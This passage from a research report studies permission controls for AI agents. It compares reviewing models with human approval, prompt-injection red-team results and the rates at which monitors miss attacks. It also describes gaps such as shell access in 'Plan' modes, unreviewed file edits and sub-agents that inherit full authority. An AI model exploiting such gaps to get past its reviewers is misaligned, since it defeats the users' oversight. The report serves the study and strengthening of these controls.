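| Nothing extra | 38.4% | 18.8% |
| Irrelevant label | 42.5% | 19.5% |
| Privilege label | 19.1% | 21.5% |
| Instruction | 9.9% | 39.5% |
| Label and instruction | 2.9% | 51.1% |

The privilege label halved the early use of stronger tools but barely changed how often the agent avoided them altogether. The agent typically tried each of the three weaker tools once, got a temporary error each time, and then used the same stronger tool as before. When also given the instruction, it more often retried a weaker tool, which always works on the second attempt. Labels alone similarly delayed the use of stronger tools by three other models.

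This also shows that ToolPrivBench's measure is lenient, since it does not count cases where the agent uses a stronger tool after trying every weaker one. With no label or instruction, Kimi K2.5 used a stronger tool too early in 18.0% of scenarios but used one at some point in 87.3%. Claude Sonnet 4.6 rarely used one but completed only 19.9% of the tasks. It usually tried each weaker tool once and then stopped to report the errors. That is safe, but Doe would still have to finish the job or tell it to try again.

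The labels were also unusually good. Their costs separated weaker from stronger tools in every scenario, which real labels probably wouldn't do. On two small models, most of the benefit remained when 30% of the costs were random. Agents therefore keep following labels that are partly wrong, so a deployment would have to stop attackers from editing them.

### Elastic least privilege

Three of the same researchers proposed a larger change that month, in the paper that uses the GitHub token as its example. Under what Parkinson and colleagues call elastic least privilege, people set outer limits in advance, and the agent gains and gives up permissions within them as it works. The design has five parts:

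- The baseline is the small set of permissions that the agent always holds.
- The envelope is the most it can obtain without a change of policy. The agent's owner sets it.
- The ceiling is a list of operations and combinations that the agent may never have, such as all three properties in Meta's Rule of Two.
- A lease is a time limit on each extra permission. In the paper's example, the agent can hold a read permission for up to 60 minutes and a write permission for up to 20.
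- The budget pays for the extra permissions, minute by minute, and refills slowly. If it runs out, the agent loses all of them at once.

A separate program issues the credentials and enforces these limits, so they don't depend on the agent's cooperation. The program also shows the agent what each option would cost and what its unused permissions are costing, and the agent can hand a permission back early to save money. Leaving out a surcharge for repeated requests, the formula is:

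```
cost per minute = (sum of weights) × 1 / (1 - p)
```

Reading has a weight of 1, writing 3 and administering 9. The value p measures how close the session is to the ceiling. It is the share of a forbidden combination that the session has already acquired.

Suppose Doe's agent has read public issues and must now fix the failing build in a public repository. Public issues are untrusted input, so the session has one of the Rule of Two's three properties. That makes p = 1/3 and the multiplier 1.5, so reading the code uses 1 × 1.5 = 1.5 units of the budget a minute. Write access to a public repository adds a second property, a way to send information out. This raises p to 2/3 and the multiplier to 3, so holding both permissions uses (1 + 3) × 3 = 12 units a minute. A third property would make p = 1 and the rate infinite, and the program rejects such a request whatever the budget.

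If the agent asked for read and write permissions at the start and kept both for 20 minutes, it would use 240 units. It could instead read for six minutes to find the fault, which would use 9 units, and then hold both permissions for six minutes to make the repair. With the surcharge for a second request, each minute of the repair would use 14 units, for a total of 93. This plan is also safer, because the agent can write for six minutes instead of 20.

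Parkinson and colleagues also simulated an attack like the one Invariant Labs demonstrated on GitHub. The hijacked agent requests access to one private repository after another, at a rising price, and has access to eight when the budget runs out. It can't publish anything, because a pull request on a public repository would complete the combination that the ceiling forbids. The ceiling prevents the theft, while the budget only limits how much private code the agent can read and for how long. The ceiling would also block a user who legitimately wanted to move private code into a public repository, unless the owner approved an exception.

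Nobody has tested this proposal on working agents. Parkinson and colleagues chose the numbers to illustrate the idea, and they say that agents might ignore the costs or save units by leaving work unfinished. The experiment with labels supports part of this worry, since visible costs alone mostly delayed the use of stronger tools, but it didn't include a budget that could run out. The limits also cover only credentials that the program issues, so an agent could use a stray token like the one at PocketOS without spending units or needing a lease.

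In 2004, JASON, a group of scientists who advise the US government, suggested pricing access to documents by giving intelligence staff a yearly supply of risk tokens, with riskier access using up more of them. Later designs let employees trade tokens in a market or punished those who overspent. The most complete, from 2012–13, gave users a budget for each period and charged extra for access outside their usual role. Its designers worried that budgeting would burden users, and that users might spend whatever was left just before it expired. An AI agent can compare prices at every step without getting tired, but someone has to make economising part of its goal.

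### Measuring false denials and leftover excess

None of these studies directly compares permissions fixed in advance with permissions adjusted during the work. Surapani and colleagues note that the field has no agreed criteria for judging least-privilege mechanisms, and they recommend measuring false denials and the burden on users as well as the attacks prevented. A comparison would also need to measure how much excess authority each approach leaves.

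Researchers could collect real requests and run each one twice, once with permissions that software fixes before the agent starts, and once with very few permissions at first, which the agent gains or loses as it works. Part of the method for measuring false denials already exists. *Permission Denied* (2026) adds operating-system limits on files, network access and privileges to an existing test of coding agents, and measures how much less they finish and how much more the work costs. However, its limits are general rather than fitted to each task.

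To measure the leftover excess, researchers could borrow a method from *Aletheia* (Shi, Chen and colleagues, 2026), which looks for suspicious permission requests in the rule files that coding agents read. The software removes one permission, runs the task again in a tighter sandbox and checks whether the result still passes its tests. If it does, the task didn't need that permission. This method would mislead where two permissions are interchangeable, because each would look unnecessary as long as the other remained. The measurement should also include time, as Parkinson and colleagues suggest, since six minutes of write access exposes less than an afternoon of it.

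If fixed permissions caused few false denials and granted little excess access, Doe's employer could issue a narrow token for each task and let the agent work mostly unsupervised. If only adjustable permissions did well, a person or a program would have to judge each request for more access, which would bring back much of the work of checking actions. The result will depend heavily on which tasks the researchers choose, and *Incomparable Minima* notes that there is no public record of what agents are asked to do.

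## Do people or models judge permission requests better?

A user can judge an agent's permission requests herself or leave them to a reviewing model. Either can make two kinds of mistake. A miss lets a harmful action through, and a false denial blocks a legitimate one. People and models are hard to compare because most studies measure only one kind of mistake or test only one kind of judge.

### How often people approve

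In March 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude Code users approved 93% of permission prompts, and in August it reported 97%. Users reject 39% of the plans that the agent presents for approval. Anthropic takes the contrast as a sign that many people approve single commands by reflex.

The contrast is weaker evidence than it looks. Most prompts concern harmless commands, so a careful user would also approve nearly all of them. OpenAI's reviewing model approves about 99% of the requests it receives, so a high approval rate doesn't have to come from boredom. And someone who rejects a plan may just want the work done differently.

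Other research, some of it from before AI agents, does point to inattention. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) cites a 2012 study by Felt and colleagues, which found that few phone users paid attention to the permission screen shown when they installed an app, and few understood it.

In *From Delegation to Action Approval*, Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) asked 203 developers how they supervise coding agents. Of these, 64% said they often approved at least one of seven kinds of action without close review. The share was 36% for access to the internet and connected tools, and 21% for reading secrets and other sensitive files. Approving some actions this way was almost as common among developers who carefully read the agent's code (61%) as among the rest (67%). It was more common among those who knew of a security or privacy problem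 involving agents (70%) than among those who didn't (43%). These are volunteers' accounts of their own habits, and they don't show how many of the approved actions were harmful.

Reviewers also seem to become more lenient toward agents with practice. Yu, Jia and colleagues (2026), in *Habituation at the Gate*, compared the early and late decisions of people who review agents' pull requests on open-source projects. The reviewers' approval rate for agents' pull requests rose from 30.1% to 36.8%, while their approval rate for other people's pull requests fell. They also put less effort into comments. This is only indirect evidence about permission prompts, because a pull request contains finished code rather than a command about to run.

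### Anthropic's test of 1,053 people

To test directly whether people pay attention to permission prompts, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor to do coding work in a test environment. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behaviour. Partway through each session, a clearly dangerous command replaced the text of one permission prompt, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the text changed, so approving it did no damage.

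The testers refused the dangerous command in 143 cases, or 13.6%. Auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%. Anthropic also reports that auto mode blocked 800 commands that a tester approved, and that testers refused six that auto mode allowed. The rest of the table follows by subtraction:

| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
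| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

Requiring approval from both would have stopped 943 commands, only six more than auto mode alone. People refused just 5% of the commands the model allowed, compared with 15% of those it blocked, so the commands that got past the model were apparently harder for people to catch too. Willison accepts that auto mode is better than constantly asking people for approval, but points out that it still missed 11% of the commands.

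Testers also refused a smaller share of dangerous commands later in a session, about 17% early on and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed flat. Each tester saw only one dangerous command, so these rates compare different people. Fatigue may explain the drop, or those who reached 50 prompts may have been quicker to approve commands from the start.

The testers weren't working on their own code and had little to lose. Doe might read more carefully if the command could delete her own database, although she might also be in more of a hurry. Anthropic gives no rate of false denials for this experiment, and a judge that refused everything would have scored 100%. Auto mode's false denials are rare in Anthropic's other data, so excessive refusal probably doesn't explain its lead.

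### When people do better

People did much better in an experiment by Yan (2026), *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*. In it, 113 people without a software background supervised an agent through a simulated day of tasks such as email and purchases. The agent proposed 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group judged every action, a second relied on automated review, and a third wrote rules in advance.

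The people who judged every action stopped about 60% of the seven, and automated review stopped about 54%. The groups were so small that this six-point gap could easily be due to chance, but it is very different from the gap in Anthropic's test.

Several differences could explain this. More than a third of the actions were out of bounds, so participants had reason to stay alert, whereas someone using Claude Code may approve hundreds of harmless commands before a bad one appears. Participants also had only 18 decisions to make. The prompts described actions such as spending money or sending a message, which are easier to understand than a shell command. The 13.6% figure for people in Anthropic's test therefore depends heavily on the conditions, and may be a poor guide to how well Doe would answer a few clear questions.

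Asking fewer questions didn't help by itself, though. Yan's third group could set "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so most of the out-of-bounds actions still reached them as prompts. They received 10.9 prompts on average instead of 18, yet stopped only about 40% of the out-of-bounds actions. Of the 148 that went through, participants had approved 133 when asked.

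Hossain and colleagues varied what the permission prompt contained. In one of their scenarios, a user allows an agent to send only summary totals to an outside auditor. A planted instruction leads the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into a file, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are permitted, so the request looks fine if the prompt describes only the sending step.

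Eighty volunteers made 12 decisions each, half of them about unsafe requests. With a conventional prompt, they approved 55.0% of the unsafe requests. The rate fell to 43.3% when the prompt included the exact details of the call, and to 32.5% when it also included the user's original restriction and a log of earlier steps. It was 24.2% with a fourth version, which contained the same facts as the third but stated their combined effect in one sentence. The last drop could be due to chance, but the overall fall suggests that people make many mistakes because the prompt leaves out what they need to know.

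Better prompts take longer to answer. The median decision time rose from 16 seconds with the conventional prompt to 33 with the fourth version, and approval of legitimate requests fell from 91.7% to 85.8%. According to Anthropic, developers may face dozens or hundreds of prompts a day. At 33 seconds each, a hundred prompts would take 55 minutes.

### Error rates of the reviewing models

Anthropic's March post reports auto mode's error rates on three sets of actions: 10,000 real tool calls by its employees, 52 real overeager actions, and 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data to outsiders. It lists rates for the fast filter alone and for the filter combined with the slower second check.

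| | Ordinary calls blocked | Overeager actions missed | Data thefts missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast filter alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Filter and second look | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second look cuts false denials about twentyfold but misses far more of the dangerous actions. Anthropic accepted this tradeoff because a reviewer that blocked one call in twelve would bring back the interruptions it was meant to remove. A false denial usually requires only a retry.

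Anthropic calls the 17% "the honest number". With only 52 cases, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. The cases came from sessions in which an employee refused the action or someone flagged it afterwards, so the sample leaves out harmful actions that nobody noticed and includes some that people had already caught.

OpenAI's figures for Auto-review look better, but they come from different tests. Trębacz and colleagues report recall, the share of dangerous actions that the reviewer denies. It was 90.3% on synthetic overeager actions and 99.3% on three kinds of prompt injection: running an attacker's code, stealing secrets and uploading data. Recall on injections fell to 90.2% when they included other categories, such as destructive deletions and tampering with data. They say most of the extra misses weren't serious and researchers often agreed with the reviewer.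 Auto-review also approved 99.1% of a sample of real requests that users had approved, so it wrongly denied about 1% if those users were right.

OpenAI used synthetic cases because its own traffic contains too few dangerous ones. OpenAI's 90.3% and auto mode's 83% don't show which product is better, because each company wrote or chose its own cases. The two reviewers also judge different actions, as Auto-review receives only requests to leave a sandbox.

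### Vague requests and hidden effects

A model reviewing permission requests does worst when the danger depends on what the user meant. In *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) gave Claude Code 128 requests that left the target, scope or risk unclear to varying degrees. In one, a user wants to cancel a stale job for a particular ticket, but other people have jobs with very similar names.

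The agent attempted 142 unsafe changes, and auto mode let 115 of them through, a miss rate of 81.0%. Of the 142, 51 were edits to files in the project folder, which by design never reach the reviewer. The reviewer received the other 91 unsafe changes and allowed 64 (70.3%). It also blocked 22 of the 69 safe changes it received (31.9%).

According to the study, these rates aren't comparable with Anthropic's 17%, because the benchmark deliberately puts permitted and forbidden targets side by side. The study also used the April version of auto mode, and Anthropic has since given the reviewer more information. Still, the results suggest that Doe has an advantage over any model, because she knows which job she meant. That knowledge helped little in Anthropic's test, where the command was plainly dangerous whatever the tester wanted. Nobody has tested people on their own vague requests.

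A command's text can also hide what it does. For example, `make clean` runs whatever steps a project's build file lists under that name, so it may delete temporary files in one project and source code in another. In *Shall We Approve?*, Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026) built 102 dangerous tasks of this kind, each with a safe version that had the same request and command but harmless code behind it. A reviewing model that read the whole conversation still let 17.6% of the dangerous tasks end in harm, and it blocked 61.8% of the safe versions.

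Their system, Caper, first runs each command in a sandbox without network access and gives the reviewer a short report of what changed. If the reviewer blocks the command, Caper restores the earlier state. Harm fell to 7.8% of the dangerous tasks, and false denials fell to 1.0% of the twins. They also ran auto mode with another company's model as the reviewer, so this test doesn't measure Anthropic's product. In that version, 62.7% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm, compared with 6.9% when Caper did the reviewing.

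Caper can't undo anything that happens outside the sandbox, and a program written to behave well on its first run might get past it. But like the people Hossain and colleagues studied, the model made fewer bad approvals when it had evidence of an action's consequences. The evidence also removed nearly all of the model's false denials.

### Attacks from outside the companies

Anthropic has paid for or invited some outside testing. Apollo Research, a British AI safety organisation, spent two weeks inserting synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. It gave Anthropic a set of attacks that had worked, and Anthropic strengthened the reviewer, mostly by giving it more information about its surroundings. Apollo then tested the new version on attacks Anthropic had never had access to. It caught about half of the attacks the old version had missed, but missed about 2% of those the old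 version had caught.

Across both sets, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. Part of that improvement comes from attacks that Anthropic had already studied, so the result on the hidden set is better evidence. Anthropic reported these numbers. Apollo Research's own account, *Red-teaming auto mode* (2026), focuses on method and open questions, including what it means for a user to authorise an action during a task that runs for hours or days. The answer affects error rates, because approving the same deletion can be counted as a miss or as correct, depending on how the user's words are interpreted.

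In a test commissioned by Anthropic, Trajectory Labs ran 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode, while 5.83% succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol with Auto-review.

The difference between the products came mainly from the agents, not their reviewers. With auto mode off and no prompts, attacks on the latest Claude models succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average, so the reviewer had almost nothing to stop. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol without its reviewer succeeded 19.03% of the time, which means that Auto-review prevented roughly two thirds of them. The attack writers had tuned their attacks against an older Claude model, and OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published the results.

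Ten runs of one scenario also aren't ten independent attacks. If runs of the same scenario tend to end the same way, the result is closer to zero successes in 72 independent trials, which is compatible with a true success rate of a few per cent. Willison wanted more independent confirmation before believing that Anthropic had solved the problem. According to The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code*, the security researcher Johann Rehberger later reported an attack on auto mode that worked in 60% to 80% of a small number of attempts. He paraphrased Anthropic's reply as saying that auto mode is a convenience feature with a best-effort classifier, "not a security guarantee."

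### Harm in real sessions

The only comparison from real work covers sessions from May and June 2026 that Anthropic's safety system had flagged for review. They came from accounts whose owners had agreed to let Anthropic use their data. A model graded each session on how much harm the agent did and how clearly the user had asked for it. The agent did serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested, such as deleting rows from a production database, in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. The rate was higher with manual approval at every level of severity.

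These were people's own projects, which answers one objection to the experiment with paid testers. But flagged sessions are a selected sample. If the safety system flags many auto mode sessions for minor reasons, the share with serious harm would be lower in auto mode even if auto mode did just as much damage overall. Anthropic would have to publish the rate of serious harm among all sessions to rule this out. Users also chose their own mode, and those who kept manual prompts may have done so because they were working on riskier systems.

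Anthropic also describes three actions that auto mode stopped inside the company. In one, an employee asked for read-only access to billing, and the agent chose a role with full administrative control. These cases show that the reviewer can catch serious mistakes, but a careful person might have caught them too.

Most of the favourable evidence comes from Anthropic, which designed or commissioned the tests, chose which results to publish and sells the product. Still, the gap between 13.6% and 89% is too large to be explained by how the results were presented, and it is strong evidence that a reviewing model is better than a distracted person at stopping plainly dangerous commands. There is no comparable result for vague requests, or for a person who gets a few well-explained questions.

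### An experiment on real work

A company with many users could answer much of this question by randomly assigning volunteers to manual prompts, a reviewing model, or a reviewing model that passes a few unclear cases to the user. The volunteers would do their ordinary work, and graders who didn't know the assignments would look for harm in a random sample of all sessions, flagged or not. The company would also count false denials and measure the time users spent on prompts.

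Some people in the manual group would turn the prompts off. The analysis should still count them in that group, because turning prompts off is one of the effects of being prompted.

Serious harm is rare, so the trial would have to be large. If harm occurs in one in a thousand sessions with manual prompts, and a reviewing model cuts that rate by 60%, detecting the difference reliably would take roughly 30,000 graded sessions in each group. A trial of that size would be difficult for a university but manageable for Anthropic or OpenAI.

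Few volunteers in a randomized trial would encounter an attacker, so the trial wouldn't measure resistance to attacks. To measure that, outsiders would need to keep sets of attacks hidden from all developers, run them against every product and against people using manual prompts, and publish the results regardless of who does well. They would also need to replace the attacks regularly and adapt them to each defence, as a real attacker would. Apollo's hidden set was a small version of this, and Apollo plans further campaigns when companies release new reviewers.

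## Do the restrictions in use reduce what an agent can do?

An approval prompt protects Doe only if her agent cannot act without approval. If the agent asks to delete a folder with one tool but could delete it without review using another, careful review of the request by Doe or a model gives her little protection.

A control can prevent an agent from causing an outcome, or it can require someone else's consent to that outcome. *AuthorityLens* (Chen, Jing and colleagues, 2026) illustrates the difference with a bank. Suppose an employee who handles complaints can compensate clients on her own. If the bank takes away her access to payments, she can't compensate anyone. If it instead requires a colleague to approve each payment, she can still compensate clients, but only with the colleague's consent. If it closes one payment system to her but leaves another open, she can still compensate clients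 without anyone's consent.

Requiring a colleague's consent for an agent's payments protects less than removing the agent's access to payments, because the colleague has to notice a bad one. But the agent can still make good payments with consent.

### Counting outcomes and participants

Chen and colleagues listed 599 outcomes, such as deleting a file outside the workspace or reading a credentials file. Each outcome is defined by its result, whatever tool the agent uses. For example, a credential counts as replaced only if the new one works and the old one doesn't.

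For each outcome, they looked for the smallest group of participants that could bring it about. A participant can be the agent, the user or a reviewing model. They then calculated two measures, which they call System Authority and Authority Separation:

```
reach = outcomes that some group can bring about / all outcomes

average participants = total size of the smallest groups
                       / outcomes within reach
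```

Suppose the list had only four outcomes: editing a file in Doe's project, running her tests, deleting a folder elsewhere on her disk, and changing her password. Her agent can edit the file and run the tests on its own, can delete the folder only with her approval, and can't change the password. Its reach is 3/4, or 75%, and the average number of participants across those three outcomes it can reach is (1 + 1 + 2) / 3 = 1.33.

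If Doe turns off approvals, the reach stays at 75% and the average falls to 1. If she instead blocks every way of deleting the folder, the reach falls to 50% and the average again falls to 1. The average therefore means little without the reach, since the average falls both when an agent gains independence and when it can no longer achieve the outcomes that needed consent.

Chen and colleagues applied these measures to 13 configurations of three coding agents: Codex, Google's Gemini CLI, and the open-source OpenCode. They read the source code, carried out the operations in test environments, and supplied the approvals themselves. The table leaves out the four configurations that use Gemini CLI's optional reviewing model.

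| Configuration | Agent alone | Agent and one other | Out of reach | Average participants |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Codex, user approves | 318 | 279 | 2 | 1.47 |
| Codex, model approves | 318 | 279 | 2 | 1.47 |
| Codex, Full Access | 599 | 0 | 0 | 1.00 |
| OpenCode, Build | 537 | 0 | 62 | 1.00 |
| OpenCode, Plan | 537 | 0 | 62 | 1.00 |
| Gemini CLI, Default | 79 | 473 | 47 | 1.86 |
| Gemini CLI, Auto-edit | 170 | 382 | 47 | 1.69 |
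| Gemini CLI, Yolo | 545 | 7 | 47 | 1.01 |
| Gemini CLI, Plan | 69 | 7 | 523 | 1.09 |

### Full Access in Codex

Full Access turns off Codex's sandbox, but it makes only two more outcomes possible, changing a password and activating a group membership. Its larger effect is to remove the need for approval. In the approval modes, the agent can bring about 318 of the 599 outcomes (53%) alone and needs the user or a reviewing model to agree to another 279. With Full Access, it can bring about all 599 alone. For example, it no longer needs approval to edit a file outside the workspace.

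When someone is available to approve requests, Codex's sandbox mostly divides authority and removes very little. It removes much more when nobody is available. According to OpenAI's *Subagents*, a page of Codex's documentation, an action that needs new approval fails if the run has no way to ask for it. By Chen and colleagues' counts, an agent in such a run should be able to reach only about 318 outcomes, although they didn't test this. People who want to confine agents could therefore make the same sandbox much stricter by not letting anyone grant exceptions during the run, but the agent would then fail at any task that needed one.

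The 53% depends on which outcomes are on the list. Chen and colleagues weight all of them equally, so reversing the characters in a line of text counts as much as deleting a directory tree. Adding more text-processing outcomes would make the approval modes look looser, and adding more deletions outside the workspace would make them look stricter. The comparison between modes depends less on the choice of outcomes, because every mode is measured against the same list.

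An agent doing ordinary work spends most of its time on things it can do without approval, even if many of the possible outcomes require it. On Chen and colleagues' list, 47% of outcomes need a reviewer, but in the snapshot of OpenAI's own use that Trębacz and colleagues published, about 7% of actions had to leave the sandbox.

Chen and colleagues didn't test narrower credentials. For each outcome, they fixed the account, its rights and its logins in advance and kept them the same in all 13 configurations. A token limited to one repository would prevent some outcomes in every mode, including Full Access, because the service would refuse the request.

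### Two planning modes

OpenCode and Gemini CLI both have a mode called Plan, in which the agent is supposed to study a project and propose changes without making them. In OpenCode, the agent can reach the same 537 outcomes in Plan as in Build, the ordinary working mode, and it can bring about all of them alone.

Plan blocks OpenCode's own tool for editing files but leaves the shell available, and a shell command can edit files too. OpenCode's documentation for version 2 lists Plan as unable to edit anything but plan files and adds that "Shell commands are not generally denied." Another page describes shell commands as "permission-controlled", so a user can write rules that restrict them. Plan is still useful for keeping a cooperative agent on task, but by itself it doesn't stop a hijacked agent from changing the user's files.

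Gemini CLI's Plan mode removes the shell, which reduces the number of outcomes the agent can reach from 552 to 76. The agent can bring about 69 of these on its own, all by reading. Removing the shell has such a large effect because this one tool gives access to programs for managing files, databases, networks and cloud services. Counting an agent's tools is therefore a poor way to estimate its authority.

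An agent without a shell can read the code behind a failing build but can't run the build to find out whether a repair works.

Users can also change what the mode allows. According to Google's *Plan Mode*, approvals given in other modes don't carry over to Plan, but a custom rule that doesn't name a mode applies in every mode. Chen and colleagues' result covers only the built-in policy, so a user with such rules may have a less restricted agent.

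In Gemini CLI's other modes, the controls change whose consent is needed but not what the agent can do. The agent can reach 552 outcomes in each of Default, Auto-edit and Yolo, but the number that need the user's consent falls from 473 to 382 to 7. Google's optional reviewer, which uses the Conseca design for deriving policies from a task, raises the average number of participants needed per outcome by almost one in each of these modes. In Default, the average rises from 1.86 to 2.84 because most outcomes then need the agent, the reviewer and the user.

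The average may overstate the protection because it counts a reviewer who approves everything as one participant, the same as a reviewer who reads every command. Anthropic found that Claude Code's users approve 97% of prompts.

These results apply to the versions that Chen and colleagues examined, and products change quickly. On 18 June 2026, Google stopped serving Gemini CLI to people with individual, Pro and Ultra accounts and directed them to Antigravity, a newer family of products that the study didn't cover, according to Google's *Gemini Code Assist consumer accounts*. If Chen and colleagues missed a way to bring about an outcome, their figures can only understate the agent's reach and overstate the number of participants an outcome needs.

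### More agents, same authority

Many coding agents can start sub-agents to share the work. Chen and colleagues found that a sub-agent usually gets a copy of the original agent's authority, rather than a separate part of it, as when a company has one employee prepare payments and another release them.

They measured this with a score for each participant. An agent earns 1 for an outcome it can bring about alone, 1/2 if it needs one other participant, 1/3 if it needs two, and nothing if it can't contribute. The score is the average over all 599 outcomes. For Codex in its approval modes:

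```
(318 × 1 + 279 × 1/2) / 599 = 0.764
```

Each sub-agent that Codex starts also scores 0.764, and the main agent's score doesn't fall. If the agents had needed each other's agreement, both scores would have been lower. With ten sub-agents, eleven agents could each bring about the same 318 outcomes alone, and an attacker would need to hijack only one of them.

Giving a sub-agent a copy of its parent's authority doesn't break the attenuation rule, which allows the two to have equal authority. According to OpenAI's documentation, a Codex sub-agent inherits its parent's sandbox policy. A user can mark a particular sub-agent as read-only, but choices the user has made during the session, such as turning off the sandbox, override the default in the sub-agent's own file.

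In the version of OpenCode that Chen and colleagues examined, even Explore, a sub-agent for searching code, could bring about all 537 outcomes alone because it had shell access. This may no longer be true, since OpenCode's documentation for version 2 lists only reading and searching tools for Explore. Gemini CLI already limited its equivalent, Investigator, to reading, and Investigator scored 0.115. These differences suggest that copying authority to a helper is a design choice, and that developers can give a helper less authority when its job is narrow.

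A reviewer may also be able to act without the agent. Codex's reviewer model can run commands to investigate requests, under a profile meant to be read-only. Chen and colleagues found that it could bring about 134 of the outcomes without the agent, 104 of them by reading. Running commands gives the reviewer more evidence, but an attacker who hijacked it could run them too, as well as decide on requests.

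### Checks that cover only some routes

Ji and colleagues found a gap in Claude Code's auto mode, which sends most shell commands to a reviewing model but lets the agent edit files in the project folder without review. In their deliberately ambiguous tasks, 36.8% of the 253 actions that changed something were these unreviewed edits. When the command-line tool the agent expected to use was missing, it often made the same change by editing a file. In tasks about cleaning up old material, 92.9% of the unsafe changes were not blocked.

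Version control can usually undo an edit to source code, but it helps less when a file in the project folder controls something outside that folder.

A sandbox is less exposed to this problem because it limits what a program can reach, whichever command started it. Chen and colleagues found weaknesses in the command checks of Codex and OpenCode and reported them privately to the developers in September 2026. In Codex, the weakness let the agent make some deletions inside the workspace without a reviewer. Deletions outside the workspace still needed one, because the sandbox blocked them. OpenCode doesn't sandbox its shell, so it had no second barrier when its check failed.

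### How often agents try

An agent may never try to do something that it could do alone. *Markdown Is Not a Firewall* (Dhuri, 2026) measured how often coding agents cross a boundary when their developers' permission prompts are off. Claude Code, Codex and OpenCode (running a DeepSeek model) worked on small programming tasks with a built-in temptation to cross one. In some tasks, a service refused a request, and the project's files described an older route marked "do not use". Others offered a destructive shortcut or contained a planted instruction.

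In most runs, a gate between the agent and a mock service blocked forbidden requests and recorded each attempt, using a filter with no model in it. Agents tried to cross a boundary in five of the 90 steps with the gate in place, and the gate blocked every attempt. Forbidden requests reached the service in seven of the 45 runs without the gate, although the service refused them in three of those seven.

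Attempts were uncommon, but frequent enough to matter to someone who runs an agent hundreds of times a week. All five blocked attempts came from OpenCode with DeepSeek, but there were too few runs to rank the products. The tasks also gave agents more reasons to make such attempts than ordinary work does.

Dhuri also tested a one-page file of written rules, which many teams put in a repository to guide agents. In one comparison, OpenCode worked once on each of five projects without the rules, and each time it used an access token it had found in the project. With the rules, no token reached the service in any of the five projects, but in one the agent tried to use an administrator's token from a backup file, and the gate blocked it. The rules may well have changed the agent's behaviour, though five runs can't establish that. They didn't make any outcome impossible or require anyone's consent,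 so when the agent ignored them, only the gate could stop it.

### Users who loosen the controls

Chen and colleagues examined the products' built-in modes, but many people change the settings. Anthropic reports that, as of June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule letting some shell commands run without a prompt. Most of these rules were broad. Anthropic says 5% of active users allowed any shell command and another 43% allowed an interpreter such as Python or Node, which it considers nearly equivalent because an interpreter runs whatever code the agent writes. The share of users with a rule was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks.

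A larger group, 62%, had at some point turned prompts off or clicked "don't ask again" for a shell command. That figure overstates how many gave up much protection, because it includes people who clicked only once, for a harmless command. A quarter of interactive sessions started with prompts off, which is a better measure of how often people work without them.

The security company UpGuard (2026) found similar habits in 18,470 Claude Code settings files that developers had left in public GitHub repositories. Of these, 14.5% let the agent run any Python command, 19.7% let it push code to a server, and 22.2% let it delete files. Only 1.1% contained a rule forbidding anything. These shares describe projects rather than people, and developers who publish their settings may be less careful than others. UpGuard also sells security products. But its count doesn't rely on Anthropic's data, and it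 also shows that people use the settings almost entirely to allow actions.

Claude Code encourages users to grant broad permissions. UpGuard explains that when a user keeps approving similar commands, the software offers to save a rule. The rule has to cover commands that differ slightly, so it may allow a program to run with any arguments. The user accepts it to avoid one kind of prompt, but it stays in the settings for every later task in that project.

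Codex has a similar feature. OpenAI recommends rules for particular commands as "often a better fit than broadly expanding access". This is good advice when the rules are narrow, but the Python rules that Trębacz and colleagues found among OpenAI's own staff were much broader.

A rule that allows commands in advance replaces consent to each action with a single consent. Chen and colleagues count a user as a participant in an outcome only if it needs a fresh decision from her. If Doe's Codex settings allow every Python command outside the sandbox, her agent no longer needs her approval for anything Python can do there. It could then bring about many of the 279 shared outcomes alone, though nobody has measured how many. Her settings would still show the approval mode, even though the agent's authority would be much closer to Full Access.

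Anthropic's figures come from an article promoting auto mode, which partly addresses the problem by suspending such broad rules. The rules take effect again when the user switches to another mode.

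## Does an agent act as its user or as a separate party?

A shop's website has no access to the settings on Doe's computer. When an order arrives from her account, the shop has her login and card number, but often no record of whether she or her agent placed it. Whether the shop should have that record depends on whether the agent counts as part of Doe or as a separate party.

Some people treat the agent as Doe's instrument, like her browser. On this view, the agent may do anything she may do, and its orders count as hers. The shop deals only with her and has no right to refuse her agent. This arrangement needs no cooperation from the shop, so it already works on most websites.

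In its 2026 guidance for companies, Microsoft advises treating every agent as a separate party, or "first-class principal". Each agent gets its own identity, so a service can refuse the agent without refusing its user, and the user's employer can shut the agent off without locking the user out. Microsoft tells companies to rehearse that shutdown and to make sure it also cancels tokens already issued. It warns against letting several agents share one secret, because nobody can then tell which of them acted.

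The difference is easy to write in the notation of the intersection rule, where U is the set of permissions Doe holds and D the set she has delegated. (She is shopping for herself here, so her employer's limits drop out.) Let S be the set of permissions that the service is willing to give this particular agent:

```
agent as instrument:       U ∩ D
agent as separate party:   U ∩ D ∩ S
```

An agent can have its own identity and still use Doe's authority, and a token naming both of them expresses this. The two views are therefore less opposed in engineering than they sound. The dispute is over whether a service may set S to nothing. This rarely causes trouble inside a company, because the employer typically controls both the agent and many of the services it uses, but a shop and the maker of a shopping agent may be competitors.

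### Amazon's demand and lawsuit

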